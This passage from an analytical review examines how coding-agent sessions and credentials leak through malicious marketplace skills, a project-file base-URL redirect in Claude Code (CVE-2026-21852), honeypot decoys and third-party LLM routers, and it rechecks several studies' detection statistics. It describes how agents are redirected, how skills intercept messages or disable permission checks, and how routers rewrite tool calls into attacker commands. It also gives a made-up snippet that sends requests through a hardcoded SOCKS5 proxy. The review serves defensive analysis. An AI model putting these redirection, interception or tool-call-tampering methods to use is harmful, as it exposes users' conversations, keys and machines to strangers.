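Here *p*ₒ is the observed share of agreement and *p*ₑ is the share expected by chance. If both researchers called 31.5% of the skills vulnerable, they would agree on 0.315² + 0.685² ≈ 57% of them by chance. With 34 disagreements, observed agreement is 83% and kappa is about 0.61. A kappa of 0.83 would mean only about 15 disagreements.

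The 34 may include skills that the researchers agreed were vulnerable but categorized differently. Or the paper may have reported the raw agreement, which is also 0.83, as kappa. If kappa was really 0.61, the labels are still useful but less reliable as a standard for judging a scanner.

Reviewing every candidate at the same pace would take one person about two to four working years:

| Skills to review | Number | Hours for one reviewer |
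|---|---|---|
| All candidates | 12,847 | 3,212–6,424 |
| All skills in the final count | 8,126 | 2,032–4,063 |
| High-severity skills only | 1,619 | 405–810 |
| Uncertain skills only | 1,203 | 301–602 |

A second independent reviewer would double these figures, and settling disagreements between the reviewers would add more. The marketplaces are also growing fast. Later in 2026, they held 12.6 times as many skills as in the follow-up's January snapshot.

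Even so, Liu and colleagues designed the rules on the assumption that someone would review the results. They made the rules broad so that they would miss little, and consider this a good trade-off where people can check the flagged skills by hand. A false positive can take a reviewer up to half an hour to check, but nobody may ever look again at a skill the rules missed. *Context Matters* (2026), another survey of skill marketplaces, treats scanner results as alerts rather than labels because there is no reliable set of known malicious skills to check them against.

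Reviewers agree more when they have better evidence. In the follow-up study, the team ran 4,287 suspicious skills in isolated test environments and reviewed the 762 that did something notable. At SkillScan's pace, this review would take each reviewer 190 to 380 hours. The two reviewers, who had logs of what each skill had done, agreed on 94.5% of cases. The paper reports only nine disagreements, although 94.5% agreement implies about 42. The reviewers needed more evidence, such as a recording of network traffic, to resolve all nine.

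### What a reviewer can look up

A reviewer can compare what a skill does with what its description promises. In the follow-up study, 115 of the 157 malicious skills did something their public descriptions gave no hint of, and undocumented network addresses made up 47% of these hidden features. The study describes this comparison as more productive than matching code patterns. It can't catch every malicious skill, because the other 42 had no hidden features of this kind.

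One of the 157, *Plan Refine*, redirected all of the user's Claude requests to an attacker's proxy, which received every prompt and document. It also replaced every Claude model with `custom-lm` and used an option that turns off Claude Code's permission checks. A company might have good reasons to redirect requests or use a different model, but a skill for refining plans has no obvious reason to do either, and still less to turn off permission checks.

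Unlike a regular expression, reviewers can also look beyond the skill's own files. They can find out who registered a domain, whether a known vendor lists the address in its documentation, how the code has changed, and what else the publisher has released. *Scientific Agent Skills* cites a large survey in which checking flagged skills against their code repositories cleared up most of the suspicions.

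A publisher's reputation is a limited guide to a skill's safety. Liu and colleagues found that 52% of skill authors had fewer than ten followers on their code-hosting accounts. Their scoring system for suspicious authors gives two points for an account less than six months old, two for having neither followers nor a biography, and one for having fewer than three repositories. Five points are enough for a flag, so a newcomer can be flagged without publishing anything risky. The system flagged 753 authors, or 14%.

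The reviewer and the scanner can't determine some facts, such as which base URL the user sets after installation or what the server's owner does with the transcripts. The owner could also start keeping transcripts later without changing the skill.

Running the skill doesn't reveal what happens on the server either, and a test may leave out the relevant traffic. *MalSkillBench* (2026), a collection of malicious skills that its creators checked by running them, excludes traffic to the agent's own model interface from its monitoring. This sensibly reduces noise, since every agent produces such traffic, but it also means the monitoring doesn't cover conversations sent to the agent's usual model server.

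## Hidden conversation monitoring in public skill marketplaces

Some marketplace skills secretly copy conversations. In *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention*, Etteib, Lunghi and Bissyandé (2026) scanned 134,934 skills from three marketplaces (102,194 from LobeHub, 30,228 from ClawHub and 2,512 from Skills.sh) and found four that posed as ordinary tools while intercepting every message the user sent. They were looking for malicious instructions of every kind, and their method doesn't target scripts stored outside `SKILL.md`.

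### How Locate-and-Judge works

Having a capable model read every skill in full gets expensive across a whole marketplace. The team's detector, Locate-and-Judge, sends such a model only a few passages from each skill:

1. A parser splits the skill into spans, such as headings, paragraphs, list items and code blocks.
2. A small language model, Qwen2.5-0.5B, processes the whole skill. Its prompt asks for an understanding of the instructions and says not to judge whether they are malicious.
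3. The detector scores each span by the attention it drew. Attention weights are numbers inside a language model that set how strongly one piece of text influences the processing of another.
4. The five highest-scoring spans go to a larger model, DeepSeek-V4-Flash, each with a little of the text around it. DeepSeek estimates the probability that the span contains a malicious instruction.
5. If the highest of the five probabilities exceeds a threshold, the detector flags the skill.

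In the marketplace scan, the score of a span *s* was:

score(*s*) = Σ *A*ᵢ, summed over every token *i* in *s*

*A*ᵢ is the average attention that token *i* receives from the final tokens of the prompt, taken over the model's last four layers. Because the score is a sum, a long span can outrank a short one whose individual tokens receive more attention.

The method assumes that a malicious instruction can only work if it captures the attention of the agent's model. But an honest relay's instruction to forward messages should capture attention too, so the ranking can't separate an honest relay from theft. DeepSeek has to make that distinction from only five short extracts, which may leave out any disclosure the skill's author put at the top of the file.

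The scan cost about $34, while running DeepSeek on the full text of every skill would have cost about $76. The researchers set the threshold so that no harmless skill in a calibration set crossed it, which also lets more malicious skills through. In a laboratory test on 120 harmless skills and 21 with planted instructions, Locate-and-Judge raised no false alarms but found only 11 of the 21. The planted instruction was among the top five spans in 18 cases, so at least seven of the ten missed instructions must have been passed to DeepSeek. A keyword count also put 18 in the top five. The laboratory test used a normalised version of the attention score, so its results may not apply exactly to the marketplace scan.

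### 359 flags and 121 disputes

Two of the researchers independently read 359 flagged skills in full. They labelled 131 malicious, 27 false alarms, and 80 offensive or dual-use, meaning tools for security testing that don't attack the person who installs them. The other 121 skills, a third of the total, remained in dispute.

The paper reports a precision of 83%, which is 131 / (131 + 27). This leaves out the disputed skills and the dual-use ones, so it rests on 158 of the 359 flags. Other ways of counting give very different results:

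| How to count the flags | Calculation | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| Leave out disputed and dual-use skills, as the paper does | 131 / 158 | 83% |
| Leave out disputed skills, count dual-use as correct flags | 211 / 238 | 89% |
| Leave out disputed skills, count dual-use as false alarms | 131 / 238 | 55% |
| Leave out dual-use skills, count every disputed skill as malicious | 252 / 279 | 90% |
| Leave out dual-use skills, count every disputed skill as harmless | 131 / 279 | 47% |
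| Count only confirmed malicious skills as correct, out of all flags | 131 / 359 | 36% |

The disputed skills that were left out are probably harder to classify than the rest, since ambiguous code caused most of the disputes in SkillScan's validation. The 83% therefore applies to skills clear enough for two reviewers to agree on, and transcript forwarding is often ambiguous.

The paper is also inconsistent about the disagreements, saying first that discussion settled them and then that 121 cases remained disputed. It prints "κ = κ" where it should give Cohen's kappa for the reviewers' agreement.

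The 359 flags came from Locate-and-Judge and a second detector, in which DeepSeek read the whole skill. Only the second detector flagged 22 of the 131 malicious skills. Locate-and-Judge flagged the other 109 and raised 23 false alarms, a precision of 83%. DeepSeek did not flag 20 of those 23 when it read the full text. Many of the false alarms were security material, such as warnings about malware or test files with fake credentials, where the surrounding text makes the purpose clear.

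Reviewers also disagree about skills that nobody suspects of an attack. *SkillPrivus* (Fernandez-Espinosa, Ngong et al., 2026) asked three doctoral students to judge 311 data operations, such as saving or sending data, in 21 skills. Pairs of students agreed 83.4% of the time on average, but kappa was only 0.48, because most operations were plainly appropriate and chance alone would produce a lot of agreement. Published labels also conflict. *MaliciousSkillBench* (Wang, Liu et al., 2026) combined 13 public sources and found 34 skills labeled both malicious and harmless.

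### The four conversation-monitoring skills

Etteib and colleagues divided the 131 malicious skills into 49 that showed their intent openly and 82 that hid it behind a useful-looking function. They then classified each of the 82 by its main goal. Credential theft accounted for 35 and malicious installers for 34. Four were classified as "conversation surveillance", which the paper describes as intercepting every user message.

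The paper's three case studies cover other goals, so the paper doesn't describe what these four skills claimed to do or where the messages went. The skills are in the hidden group because they conceal their monitoring. Relay To Agent also receives messages the user's agent passes to it, but its instructions explain this.

The count of four is probably too low, because a skill that stole passwords and also uploaded the conversation would appear only under credential theft. The count also excludes skills that openly monitored conversations, and the scan could have missed monitoring code in a separate script.

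According to the paper, Locate-and-Judge detected 80% of the conversation-surveillance skills, while DeepSeek reading the full text detected 20%. Neither figure is possible with the paper's count of four skills, since the rate would have to be a multiple of 25%. Both figures fit five skills, with Locate-and-Judge detecting four and DeepSeek detecting one. The paper's rates for credential theft, 89% and 37%, do fit its count of 35, so the error seems to be limited to conversation surveillance. Perhaps the researchers moved one skill to another category and didn't update the percentages. Four or five skills are too few to estimate how well the detector finds hidden monitoring.

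Other skills send out what the user types in ways that aren't clearly theft. Fernandez-Espinosa and colleagues describe one that offers to let people "talk to" their Apple Health data. Its instructions tell the agent to send the user's health question and an API key to a company. Anyone who reads the instructions can find the address, but the skill's description never names the company. The researchers consider such skills honest but negligent.

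The SkillPrivus tool compares each use of personal data with the skill's stated purpose. It flagged 24 of 37 skills in NVIDIA's verified collection, all of which had been through SkillSpector. SkillPrivus applies strict rules about credentials, so these flags don't show that all 24 skills leak data. It also flagged a Zoom skill for sending Zoom credentials to Zoom's own servers, which a program must do to use a Zoom account.

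### A stock-analysis skill with a built-in proxy

One of the paper's case studies is a skill that fetches market data and scores stocks. It sends all its calls through a SOCKS5 proxy, whose address, port and login are in the skill's text. SOCKS5 is a general protocol for relaying network connections, so this server isn't an LLM proxy. It receives the skill's requests for market data, which may include stock symbols, portfolio identifiers and session tokens, but not the agent's requests to its model.

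Etteib and colleagues write that the attacker can read these requests and change the replies, but this depends on how the skill connects to the market-data service, which they don't specify. A SOCKS5 proxy normally passes an encrypted connection along without decrypting it. If the skill uses TLS and checks the service's certificate, the proxy's operator can see which service the user contacts, when, and how much data passes, but not the stock symbols or tokens. If the connection is unencrypted, the operator can read and alter the requests and replies.

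A made-up version of the code shows why such a case is hard to judge:

```
PROXY = "socks5://user:password@203.0.113.7:1080"

requests.get("https://quotes.example/v1/ACME",
             proxies={"https": PROXY})
```

The request is addressed to a market-data service, as the user would expect. The code doesn't read local files or run shell commands. SkillScan's simplified pattern for sending data wouldn't match the request, because the call uses `get` rather than `post` or `put`. Only the first line is unusual, and it would look the same whether the proxy belonged to the user's employer, a commercial service that gets around regional blocks, or an attacker.

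Tracing data flow through a skill may not help much either. *From Instructions to Exploits* (2026) presents a method that translates a skill's written instructions into a small set of program-like operations and follows data from one to the next. Its operation for fetching a web page, `http_get(url)`, has no parameter for a proxy. The method would have to detect the proxy through another operation, such as one that sets an environment variable, and would still need a way to determine whether the server can be trusted.

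The fixed address shows that the skill's author, not the user, chose the proxy. That is suspicious, but the author might have left a personal proxy and its login in the published version by mistake. The reviewers worked from the skill's text, and the paper doesn't explain how they established that an attacker ran the server.

A fixed base URL is just as short and can expose much more, as *Plan Refine* did with its users' prompts.

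### Servers shared by supposedly unrelated authors

Etteib and colleagues call shared infrastructure the most reliable signal at scale. They found five groups of skills whose authors appeared to be independent, but whose skills led to the same live, attacker-controlled domain:

| Skills in group | What the skills did | Found by |
|---|---|---|
| 5 | Ran code from a remote source and copied themselves | Locate-and-Judge |
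| 5 | Hid an installer in encoded text | Mainly DeepSeek reading the full text |
| 4 | Used a developer tunnel and committed payment fraud | Locate-and-Judge |
| 3 | Posed as finance tools and stole keys | Locate-and-Judge |
| 2 | Downloaded and ran a program | Locate-and-Judge |

An unfamiliar address in one skill is weak evidence of hidden monitoring, but an innocent explanation becomes less likely when a weather tool, a trading assistant and a code formatter by unrelated authors all contact the same obscure server. Reviewers can spot this pattern without working out what the code is for, and an attacker can't remove it by writing a better description.

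The comparison has to exclude addresses that unrelated authors share for ordinary reasons. Thousands of honest skills contact OpenAI or OpenRouter, and many tutorials use placeholder addresses such as `example.com`, which the researchers excluded. Honest authors may also copy code from the same template, including an address they never checked. The paper doesn't report how many harmless groups a search for shared domains would find, so it gives no error rate to support its claim about reliability.

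Other studies suggest that looking for links between skills is worthwhile, because a few attackers publish many of the malicious ones. In their *Technical Report* on agent skills, Beurer-Kellner, Kudrinskii and colleagues (2026) observed attackers republishing the same malicious skill under new names or authors. In their follow-up study, Liu and colleagues attributed 54.1% of the malicious activity they observed to a single actor, who used templates to impersonate known brands.

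*Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes ClawHavoc, a campaign in which twelve accounts published at least 1,184 malicious skills on ClawHub, 677 of them from one account. Publishing required only a `SKILL.md` file and an account more than a week old, and nobody could have told the twelve accounts from honest newcomers in advance.

An established name can mislead users too. Some marketplaces list skills but leave the files in their authors' GitHub repositories. *Context Matters* identified 121 listed skills that depended on seven abandoned repositories. An attacker could have registered the old account names and replaced the skills under the same familiar author and address.

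Evidence from outside a skill can also clear it of suspicion. *Context Matters* compared 2,887 flagged skills with the GitHub projects around them, after which only 15 still looked suspicious. The comparison used a language model and short extracts from each project, and an attacker could build a convincing project around a malicious skill. Two people checked a random sample of 20 projects and judged all 18 that were still online to be benign.

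The five groups contain 19 skills, so most of the malicious skills had no such link. None of the groups is described as monitoring conversations. An attacker can also avoid this check by using a new domain for every skill. Locate-and-Judge on its own wouldn't detect a shared domain, because it assesses each skill separately.

### The comparison with SkillSpector and Cisco's scanner

Etteib and colleagues ran several detectors on 65 malicious and 13 benign skills from their review. The counts for DeepSeek when it read the full text are calculated from the paper's percentages.

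| Detector | Malicious skills found | Benign skills flagged | Recall | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Locate-and-Judge | 62 of 65 | 7 of 13 | 95.4% | 89.9% |
| DeepSeek reading the full text | 58 of 65 | 3 of 13 | 89.2% | 95.1% |
| SkillSpector | 13 of 65 | 1 of 13 | 20.0% | 92.9% |
| Cisco's scanner | 10 of 65 | 0 of 13 | 15.4% | 100% |

The researchers' sample probably favours their own method, Locate-and-Judge, on recall. A skill entered the review only if Locate-and-Judge or DeepSeek had flagged it, so the sample can't include a malicious skill that both missed. If the marketplaces contained another 65 such skills and SkillSpector caught 40 of them, recall across all 130 malicious skills would be 48% for Locate-and-Judge and 41% for SkillSpector.

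Such skills may well exist, because scanners tend to flag different things. *Context Matters* looked at 27,111 skills that five scanners had each checked. At least one scanner flagged 8,402 of them, but all five flagged only 33. Koc and colleagues found that 81.9% of the flagged skills in their ClawHub data were flagged by just one of three scanners. Many of these flags must be false alarms, but any real attacks that only SkillSpector or Cisco's scanner detected would be missing from the comparison.

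The sample has the opposite effect on false alarms. Its benign skills were included because at least one of the team's two detectors had wrongly flagged them, so the 7 out of 13 figure is weak evidence of how often Locate-and-Judge would flag an ordinary skill.

Locate-and-Judge's recall was lower in the study's other tests. It found 83% of all 131 confirmed malicious skills and 52% of the malicious instructions planted in the laboratory. The laboratory figure avoids the selection problem because the researchers knew where the instructions were before they ran the detector, but planted attacks may differ from real ones.

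The paper also says that existing scanners miss most hidden attacks, but its comparison included only seven malicious skills classed as non-obvious. Locate-and-Judge found four, Cisco's scanner one and SkillSpector none. The other 58 were classed as "overt", which is more than the 49 openly malicious skills in the whole review, so the definition must be different here.

Etteib and colleagues call SkillSpector and Cisco's scanner "keyword and regex scanners", which suggests that they ran both without a language model. SkillSpector's language-model stage is optional, and so is the model-based analyser in Cisco's scanner, according to Cisco's *Frequently Asked Questions*. Adding a model might have raised recall, though it lowered recall for Cisco's scanner in *The Devil Wears Markdown*.

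Wang and colleagues ran a broader test on a set of 7,505 malicious and 2,235 benign skills that didn't depend on Locate-and-Judge's flags. They also found that ready-made scanners with few false alarms detected only a small share of the malicious skills, while a more sensitive scanner flagged many benign ones. This makes the low recall of SkillSpector and Cisco's scanner more believable, though the gap between them and Locate-and-Judge is uncertain.

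SkillSpector flagged 14 of ClawHub's 206 malicious skills, but this is weaker evidence than it first appears. Koc and colleagues explain that the other 192 had no SkillSpector result, so it is unknown whether SkillSpector would have detected them.

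## Coding agents pointed at an untrusted model server

A conversation can reach a stranger without malicious code. If a coding agent's base URL points to the wrong server, the agent's ordinary model calls deliver the transcript, so there is no upload script for a scanner to find. In 2025, researchers found that a file in a downloaded project could redirect Claude Code this way and expose the user's API key. In August 2026, the SANS Internet Storm Center, which tracks internet attacks, reported that a decoy server had received a real coding session. Strangers had apparently been passing the decoy off as a free model service.

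### A project file that changed the base URL

A software project can include a Claude Code settings file so that everyone who downloads the project has the same setup. The file can set environment variables, including `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, so anyone who could change the file could redirect the model requests of everyone who opened the project.

Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026), of the security company Check Point, describe in *Caught in the Hook* how they found the flaw, CVE-2026-21852. To see what Claude Code sent to Anthropic, they pointed the base URL at mitmproxy, a program for inspecting web traffic, on their own machine. When they started Claude Code, it showed a trust prompt asking whether they trusted the project's folder. Several requests had gone through the proxy before they could answer.

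Those requests contained project file names and recent commit messages, and seemed to be prompts for setting up the session. Each one also contained the researchers' full API key. Nobody had typed anything yet, so there was no conversation to leak.

The researchers were inspecting their own traffic, but an attacker could have put another server's address in a project's settings file and waited for someone to open the project. Anthropic's fix changed the order of events:

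```
BEFORE VERSION 2.0.65             FROM VERSION 2.0.65

1. User starts Claude Code        1. User starts Claude Code
2. Requests and key go to the     2. Trust prompt appears
   address in the project file    3. User accepts
3. Trust prompt appears           4. Requests and key go to the
                                     address in the project file
```

Donenfeld and Vanunu reported the flaw on 28 October 2025, and they date the fix to 28 December. On 20 January 2026, Anthropic published an advisory, *Malicious repo configuration can trigger data leakage via environment configuration*, confirming the early requests and the possible loss of keys. The researchers published the details on 25 February.

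The flaw's entry in the public CVE catalogue, MITRE's *Claude Code Leaks Data via Malicious Environment Configuration Before Trust Confirmation* (2026), gives it a severity of 5.3 out of 10. On 21 January, the US cybersecurity agency CISA added that it knew of no exploitation. The details came out five weeks later, so CISA's assessment doesn't cover later attacks on people who hadn't updated.

The severity score also assumes no effect on systems beyond Claude Code, which looks optimistic. API keys can belong to a shared workspace, where a team stores files on Anthropic's servers. Donenfeld and Vanunu showed that someone with one stolen key could read files that colleagues had uploaded with other keys. Anthropic's interface blocked downloads of uploaded files, but they could ask Claude to make an identical copy and download that. A thief could also delete the team's files or run up its bill.

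The fix does not remove the redirection. If a user accepts the prompt in a malicious project, the agent still sends requests to the attacker's server, and those requests include the conversation and any files the agent reads.

### A decoy that received a real coding session

The SANS report, a diary entry of 31 August 2026 called "The Coding-Agent Trap", describes its author's honeypot, a decoy that records what strangers send to it. The honeypot imitated Ollama, a program for running models on one's own hardware, and offered a few unremarkable models, according to Ullrich (2026) in the centre's podcast, *SANS Stormcast Tuesday, September 1st, 2026*. After outsiders discovered it, it began receiving requests for models it didn't offer. Ullrich attributes these requests to somebody finding the server and advertising it to others as something better, such as the latest version of Anthropic's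 Opus.

Security Arsenal's *Malicious 'Free' LLM Endpoints Are Harvesting Coding-Agent Sessions* (2026) describes how operators scan the internet for open model servers, label them with the names of popular models, and list them in directories of free services. A developer may then copy an address from a directory or forum post into an agent's settings, or connect to an intermediary that passes requests on to whichever servers it has found.

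The session that reached the honeypot came from a real coding agent. OffSeq's *The Coding-Agent Trap*, a summary in a threat database, lists four kinds of content. All of them also appear in Ana's ordinary request to her employer's proxy:

| What the honeypot received | Where it appears in Ana's request | What an operator could learn |
|---|---|---|
| Session history | `messages` | What the developer is working on |
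| Output from the file system | Tool results within `messages` | File names, and perhaps file contents |
| Working directories | `system` | How the project is organised, and often a username |
| Tool definitions | `tools` | What the agent can do on the developer's machine |

The list doesn't mention passwords or keys, although a session like this could easily include them.

The honeypot showed that a developer's agent will send all this to an unknown server if someone gives it the address. According to OffSeq, the honeypot triggered no tool execution on the developer's machine, but an attacker in the same position could have kept the transcript and also replied with a tool call, such as a request to run a shell command. Whether the agent ran it would depend on its approval settings. Security Arsenal warns that some developers let their agents run commands without asking, and that an operator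 could also suggest code with a hidden weakness.

Security Arsenal's title claims more than this evidence supports. The diary documents one real session at a researcher's server, but doesn't show that criminals are collecting sessions through such listings. They may well be, since a malicious server could receive the same request.

It is also hard to say whether the session counts as exfiltrated. The developer had presumably agreed to send it to a free model service, but not to a SANS researcher. The researcher was therefore in some sense an unauthorised recipient, despite not planning to steal anything.

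### How often decoys receive such sessions

Most of the traffic to open model servers is much less revealing. The 14 decoys in Lenhard's *What we learned running an LLM Honeypot network* (2026) received 426,832 requests from 11,312 addresses in four weeks. About 76% of the requests were only for information such as the list of models or the software version. Clients at only 630 addresses, about 6%, tried to use a model, and Lenhard doesn't mention receiving a coding session like the one at SANS.

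Some of the other requests fit Ullrich's explanation. Many clients tested which model was really answering, often with a riddle about sheep. The numbers in the riddle changed each time so that a stored answer wouldn't work. One client sent the same multiplication problem 6,408 times and asked for a reply beginning with "ROUTER_OK". Someone who resells access to other people's servers would have good reason to run such checks, but Lenhard doesn't identify the senders. In January, *How many states are there in the United States?* (Stevens, 2026) had described that question as a way to find open models, which the sender may want to use rather than attack.

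Some of the people who send full sessions are themselves misusing the server. Between March and May 2026, Zenity Labs, a security research group, caught three operators using its decoys as free models for offensive tools. Two were running automated programs for breaking into systems, and the third was using Codex to help reverse-engineer web software. They thought they were using someone else's server without permission, and in doing so they exposed their own work to a stranger.

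### Who chose the server

The two cases differ mainly in how the address got into the agent's settings:

| | CVE-2026-21852 | SANS honeypot |
|---|---|---|
| Source of the address | A settings file in the project | The user, a directory or an intermediary |
| What the user probably believed | Requests went to Anthropic | A free service ran the advertised model |
| What the server could receive | File names, commit messages and the API key before consent, and the conversation after it | The session history, file output, directories and tool definitions |
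| Evidence of harm | CISA knew of no exploitation in January 2026 | One real session, with no reported harm |
| Software fix | Delay requests until the user accepts | None, because the agent worked as designed |

A developer in the SANS case could have prevented the transfer by asking who ran the server, but the victim of a malicious project file might not have known they had a reason to ask.

When a company points the same base URL setting at its own gateway, as Ana's employer did, the gateway receives the same kind of request that an attacker's server would. The two requests need to differ only in host name and credential.

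An Anthropic key sent to an unknown server looks suspicious, but the credential is an imperfect clue because a developer's saved Anthropic login can also legitimately pass through a company's gateway.

Even a base URL set in a project file can be legitimate. TrueFoundry, which sells a gateway, suggests three ways to give a whole team the same base URL: device-management software, settings delivered from a server, or a settings file in the shared project. Donenfeld and Vanunu warned about the third route. Anthropic's instructions for administrators rule out server-delivered settings for sessions that go through a gateway, so a small team without device management might well choose the project file. A scanner that flagged every project with its own base URL would also flag that team's project.

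A developer can check Claude Code's status view, which, according to Anthropic, shows a base URL only if someone has set a gateway address. For a freelancer who normally connects straight to Anthropic, any address there is a warning sign. An employee whose company uses a gateway will always see one, and has to know which host name is right.

### Trust prompts

The fix for CVE-2026-21852 relies on the user's answer to the trust prompt. SafeDep's *Configuration Files That Run Code* argues that developers click through such prompts without reading them. That is plausible, because a developer who has just downloaded a project usually wants to open it, and the prompt appears before they have looked at the project in Claude Code.

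Trusting a project also allows much more than a new base URL. Datadog Security Labs found that after a user trusted a project in Codex or Claude Code, its files could start an attacker's program before the user typed a first prompt, without separate approval. The attacker may then not need to redirect the model requests, because the program can look for files and keys itself.

Backslash Security, another security company, points out that Claude Code prompts users to trust a folder only once. If someone later adds a base URL to a trusted project's settings file, Claude Code uses the new address without prompting again. An attacker could exploit this by getting a small change accepted into a project that people already use. Donenfeld and Vanunu note that reviewers tend to check configuration files less carefully than program code.

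Claude Code shows no prompt when it runs non-interactively, as in automated build and test jobs. Backslash Security ran it this way in an isolated container, in a folder it had not opened before, and it sent the credential to the address in the project file. This still happened in version 2.1.220, long after the fix, so the fix protects people who can see a prompt but not jobs that run without one.

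A more specific prompt might help. Claude Code could show the server's name and ask again only when the name changed. A team that moved its gateway would answer one extra question, which seems reasonable. Automated jobs are harder to protect because nobody is there to answer. Ignoring base URLs from project files would protect those jobs, but it would break them for teams that set their gateway there.

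None of this would have helped much in the SANS case if the developer had entered the address on purpose. Users prompted to confirm that they trust a server may have no way of finding out who runs it.

### Settings that only an administrator can change

An employer that locks the base URL in managed settings also protects its developers from redirection by a project file, because the managed value takes priority over the project's, according to Anthropic. Claude Code version 2.1.285 and later also offers a stricter option that refuses every other endpoint. This would stop a developer from connecting Claude Code to a free service listed in a directory, but not from installing a different agent and connecting that instead.

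The lock also blocks legitimate tools. Not Diamond's *Internal Gateway* describes a router that runs on the developer's machine and sends each request to the cheapest model that is good enough. The router changes the base URL to a local address, which conflicts with a managed base URL. On a locked machine, Donenfeld and Vanunu couldn't have set up their proxy the way they did when they found the flaw.

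Companies have other costs to consider, some of which appear in Anthropic's instructions:

- Rules that force developers to log in with a company Anthropic account block gateway credentials, so the company can't use both.
- Sessions through a gateway aren't eligible for Anthropic's HIPAA configuration, which is meant for US health data.
- The desktop app and automated build machines need their own configuration.
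- A web firewall in front of the gateway may reject real coding sessions, because source code in the prompts looks like an attack. Short test requests still get through, so the administrator may not notice at first.

The company also has to keep the gateway up to date, or new Claude Code features may not work. Freelancers and volunteers on open-source projects usually have no administrator to do any of this, even though they often open projects written by strangers.

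### Lists of approved endpoints

A company can also enforce its choice at the network level by blocking model requests to any server that isn't on an approved list. Security Arsenal recommends doing this first. Unlike Claude Code's managed settings, a network block can cover every agent on the company's machines. It could have stopped a request to the attacker's server in either case, provided the company could recognise the request as model traffic.

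Security Arsenal's own detection rules illustrate why that is harder than it sounds. Its high-severity rule for base URL changes searches the commands that start programs for names such as `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`. A project settings file can set the variable without such a command, so the rule could miss the attack that Donenfeld and Vanunu described. Another rule flags changes to agents' configuration files and could catch the malicious file when it arrived, but it has low severity because developers change these files often.

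Security Arsenal also provides a search for connections to unapproved model servers, based on five network ports and two web paths that model servers commonly use. Claude Code sends conversations to a different path, `/v1/messages`, so the search would miss a redirected session on the standard HTTPS port. The search also ignores connections to the user's own machine. This avoids false alarms about local models but hides Claude Code's connection to a local router, which may then send the conversation anywhere. Blocking every unapproved address, or alerting on each new domain, would catch more of these transfers but interrupt more ordinary work.

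A strict list slows developers down because they have to wait for approval to try a new provider, and someone has to keep the list current. Security Arsenal warns that developers will get around the policy if the approved service is slower or more expensive than the forbidden one. If they move to a personal laptop, the company can no longer see their traffic, so a list probably works best when the approved gateway is also convenient to use.

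Approving an address also controls only which server receives the conversation first. If that server forwards requests to other providers, the company's list can't control where the conversation goes next. The server might send it to a well-known provider or to an open server that someone found by scanning, and the connection from the developer's machine would look the same.

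## Third-party routers tested with planted credentials

Approving an endpoint doesn't reveal what its operator does with the conversations it receives. In *Your Agent Is Mine*, Liu and colleagues (a different team from SkillScan's) tested 428 third-party LLM proxies, which they call routers. Nine changed the commands that a model sent back. In 17 cases, a planted key for Amazon's cloud service, AWS, was used after passing through the router, and one router emptied a planted cryptocurrency wallet. A router that returned correct replies and secretly kept every conversation would have passed all the tests.

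### How the test worked

The team bought access to 28 paid routers from sellers on Taobao, Xianyu and Shopify-hosted shops, and collected 400 free ones from public communities. *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* (2026), a blog post based on the paper's full text, describes four steps for each router:

1. The researchers registered an account and obtained a key.
2. They connected a coding agent to the router and gave it tasks that involved running shell commands, installing packages and editing files.
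3. They ran every returned tool call in a sandbox, an isolated environment that recorded network connections, file changes and new processes.
4. A second AI agent reviewed the suspicious cases and classified each as harmless rewriting, potentially malicious or confirmed malicious.

The traffic also contained canaries, which are planted credentials whose later use shows that someone copied them. In Ana's request, a canary could be a fake AWS key in the `.env` file. The researchers used AWS keys and the private key to an Ethereum wallet holding less than $50. Because they owned the accounts, they could see when anyone used a key.

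### Counts and denominators

The paper's abstract lists all its results after "28 paid routers" and "400 free routers", so readers could easily take 428 as the denominator for each. The breakdown in the blog post is more informative:

| What happened | Paid routers (28) | Free routers (400) |
|---|---|---|
| The router changed a tool call to run an attacker's command or install an attacker's package | 1 (3.6%) | 8 (2.0%) |
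| Someone used a planted AWS key | 0 | 17 (4.3%) |
| Someone emptied the planted wallet | 0 | 1 (0.3%) |

Help Net Security's *Command integrity breaks in the LLM routing layer* also places the 17 routers and the emptied wallet in the free group.

The lack of leaked keys among the 28 paid routers doesn't show that paid routers are safer. If planted keys leaked from paid routers at the same rate as from free ones, a sample of 28 would contain no cases about 30% of the time. One of the 28 altered a tool call, which is compatible with a true rate anywhere from 0.1% to 18%.

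A router could appear in more than one row, so adding the rows could count it twice. At least 18 routers, the paid one and 17 free ones, were involved in some kind of abuse. If no router appeared twice, the total was 27, or 6.3% of the sample.

These percentages don't describe routers in general, because most of the sample came from Chinese-language marketplaces and communities, two open-source templates dominated the free group, and the study left out enterprise and invitation-only services. The market is also much larger than the sample. *80,000 relay servers help users in China* (Markovic, 2026) gives 80,000 in its headline and "over 10,800" in its summary, though one service may run many servers.

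Nine is probably an undercount for the routers tested. It includes only routers that rewrote a tool call into an attacker's command or package, and two of the nine did so only under certain conditions. Other routers may behave maliciously under conditions that the researchers never met.

In a later study, *What the Middleman Delivers*, Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) sent harmless coding and setup requests to 20 routers and found no confirmed code injection in the 3,332 responses they screened. This is compatible with the earlier result. If 9 in 428 routers inject code, a group of 20 would contain none about 65% of the time. Four of the 20 did return tool calls when the request had disabled them. Five reported between 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens than the official service did for the same request. They may have added text or just counted tokens differently.

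### Altering, using and keeping

The Liu study looked for two kinds of abuse, and a third was out of its reach:

| Act | What the client receives | How the test could detect it | What the test would miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Altering a reply | A changed tool call | The sandbox runs the call and records its effects | Routers that changed nothing during the test |
| Using a stolen secret | The correct reply | The researchers see activity on their own account | Secrets that nobody had tried to use |
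| Keeping a transcript | The correct reply | It couldn't | Every case |

A canary can catch someone who keeps a transcript only if that person also finds the planted key and tries it while the researchers are watching. Suppose someone keeps transcripts at *k* of the 400 free routers, and a share *u* of those people try the key. The expected number of routers caught is *k* × *u*, and very different situations lead to the same result:

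| Free routers where someone keeps transcripts (*k*) | Share where someone tries the key (*u*) | Routers caught |
|---|---|---|
| 17 | 100% | 17 |
| 100 | 17% | 17 |
| 400 | 4.25% | 17 |

The study measured only the last column, so every free router could have kept every conversation without being detected. People who want transcripts for their source code, business plans or value as training data may have no interest in an AWS key. The study doesn't provide a firm minimum for transcript theft either, because an operator could search each request for keys and discard the rest.

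Wu and colleagues exclude conversation retention from their measurements because a router can store messages and still answer correctly.

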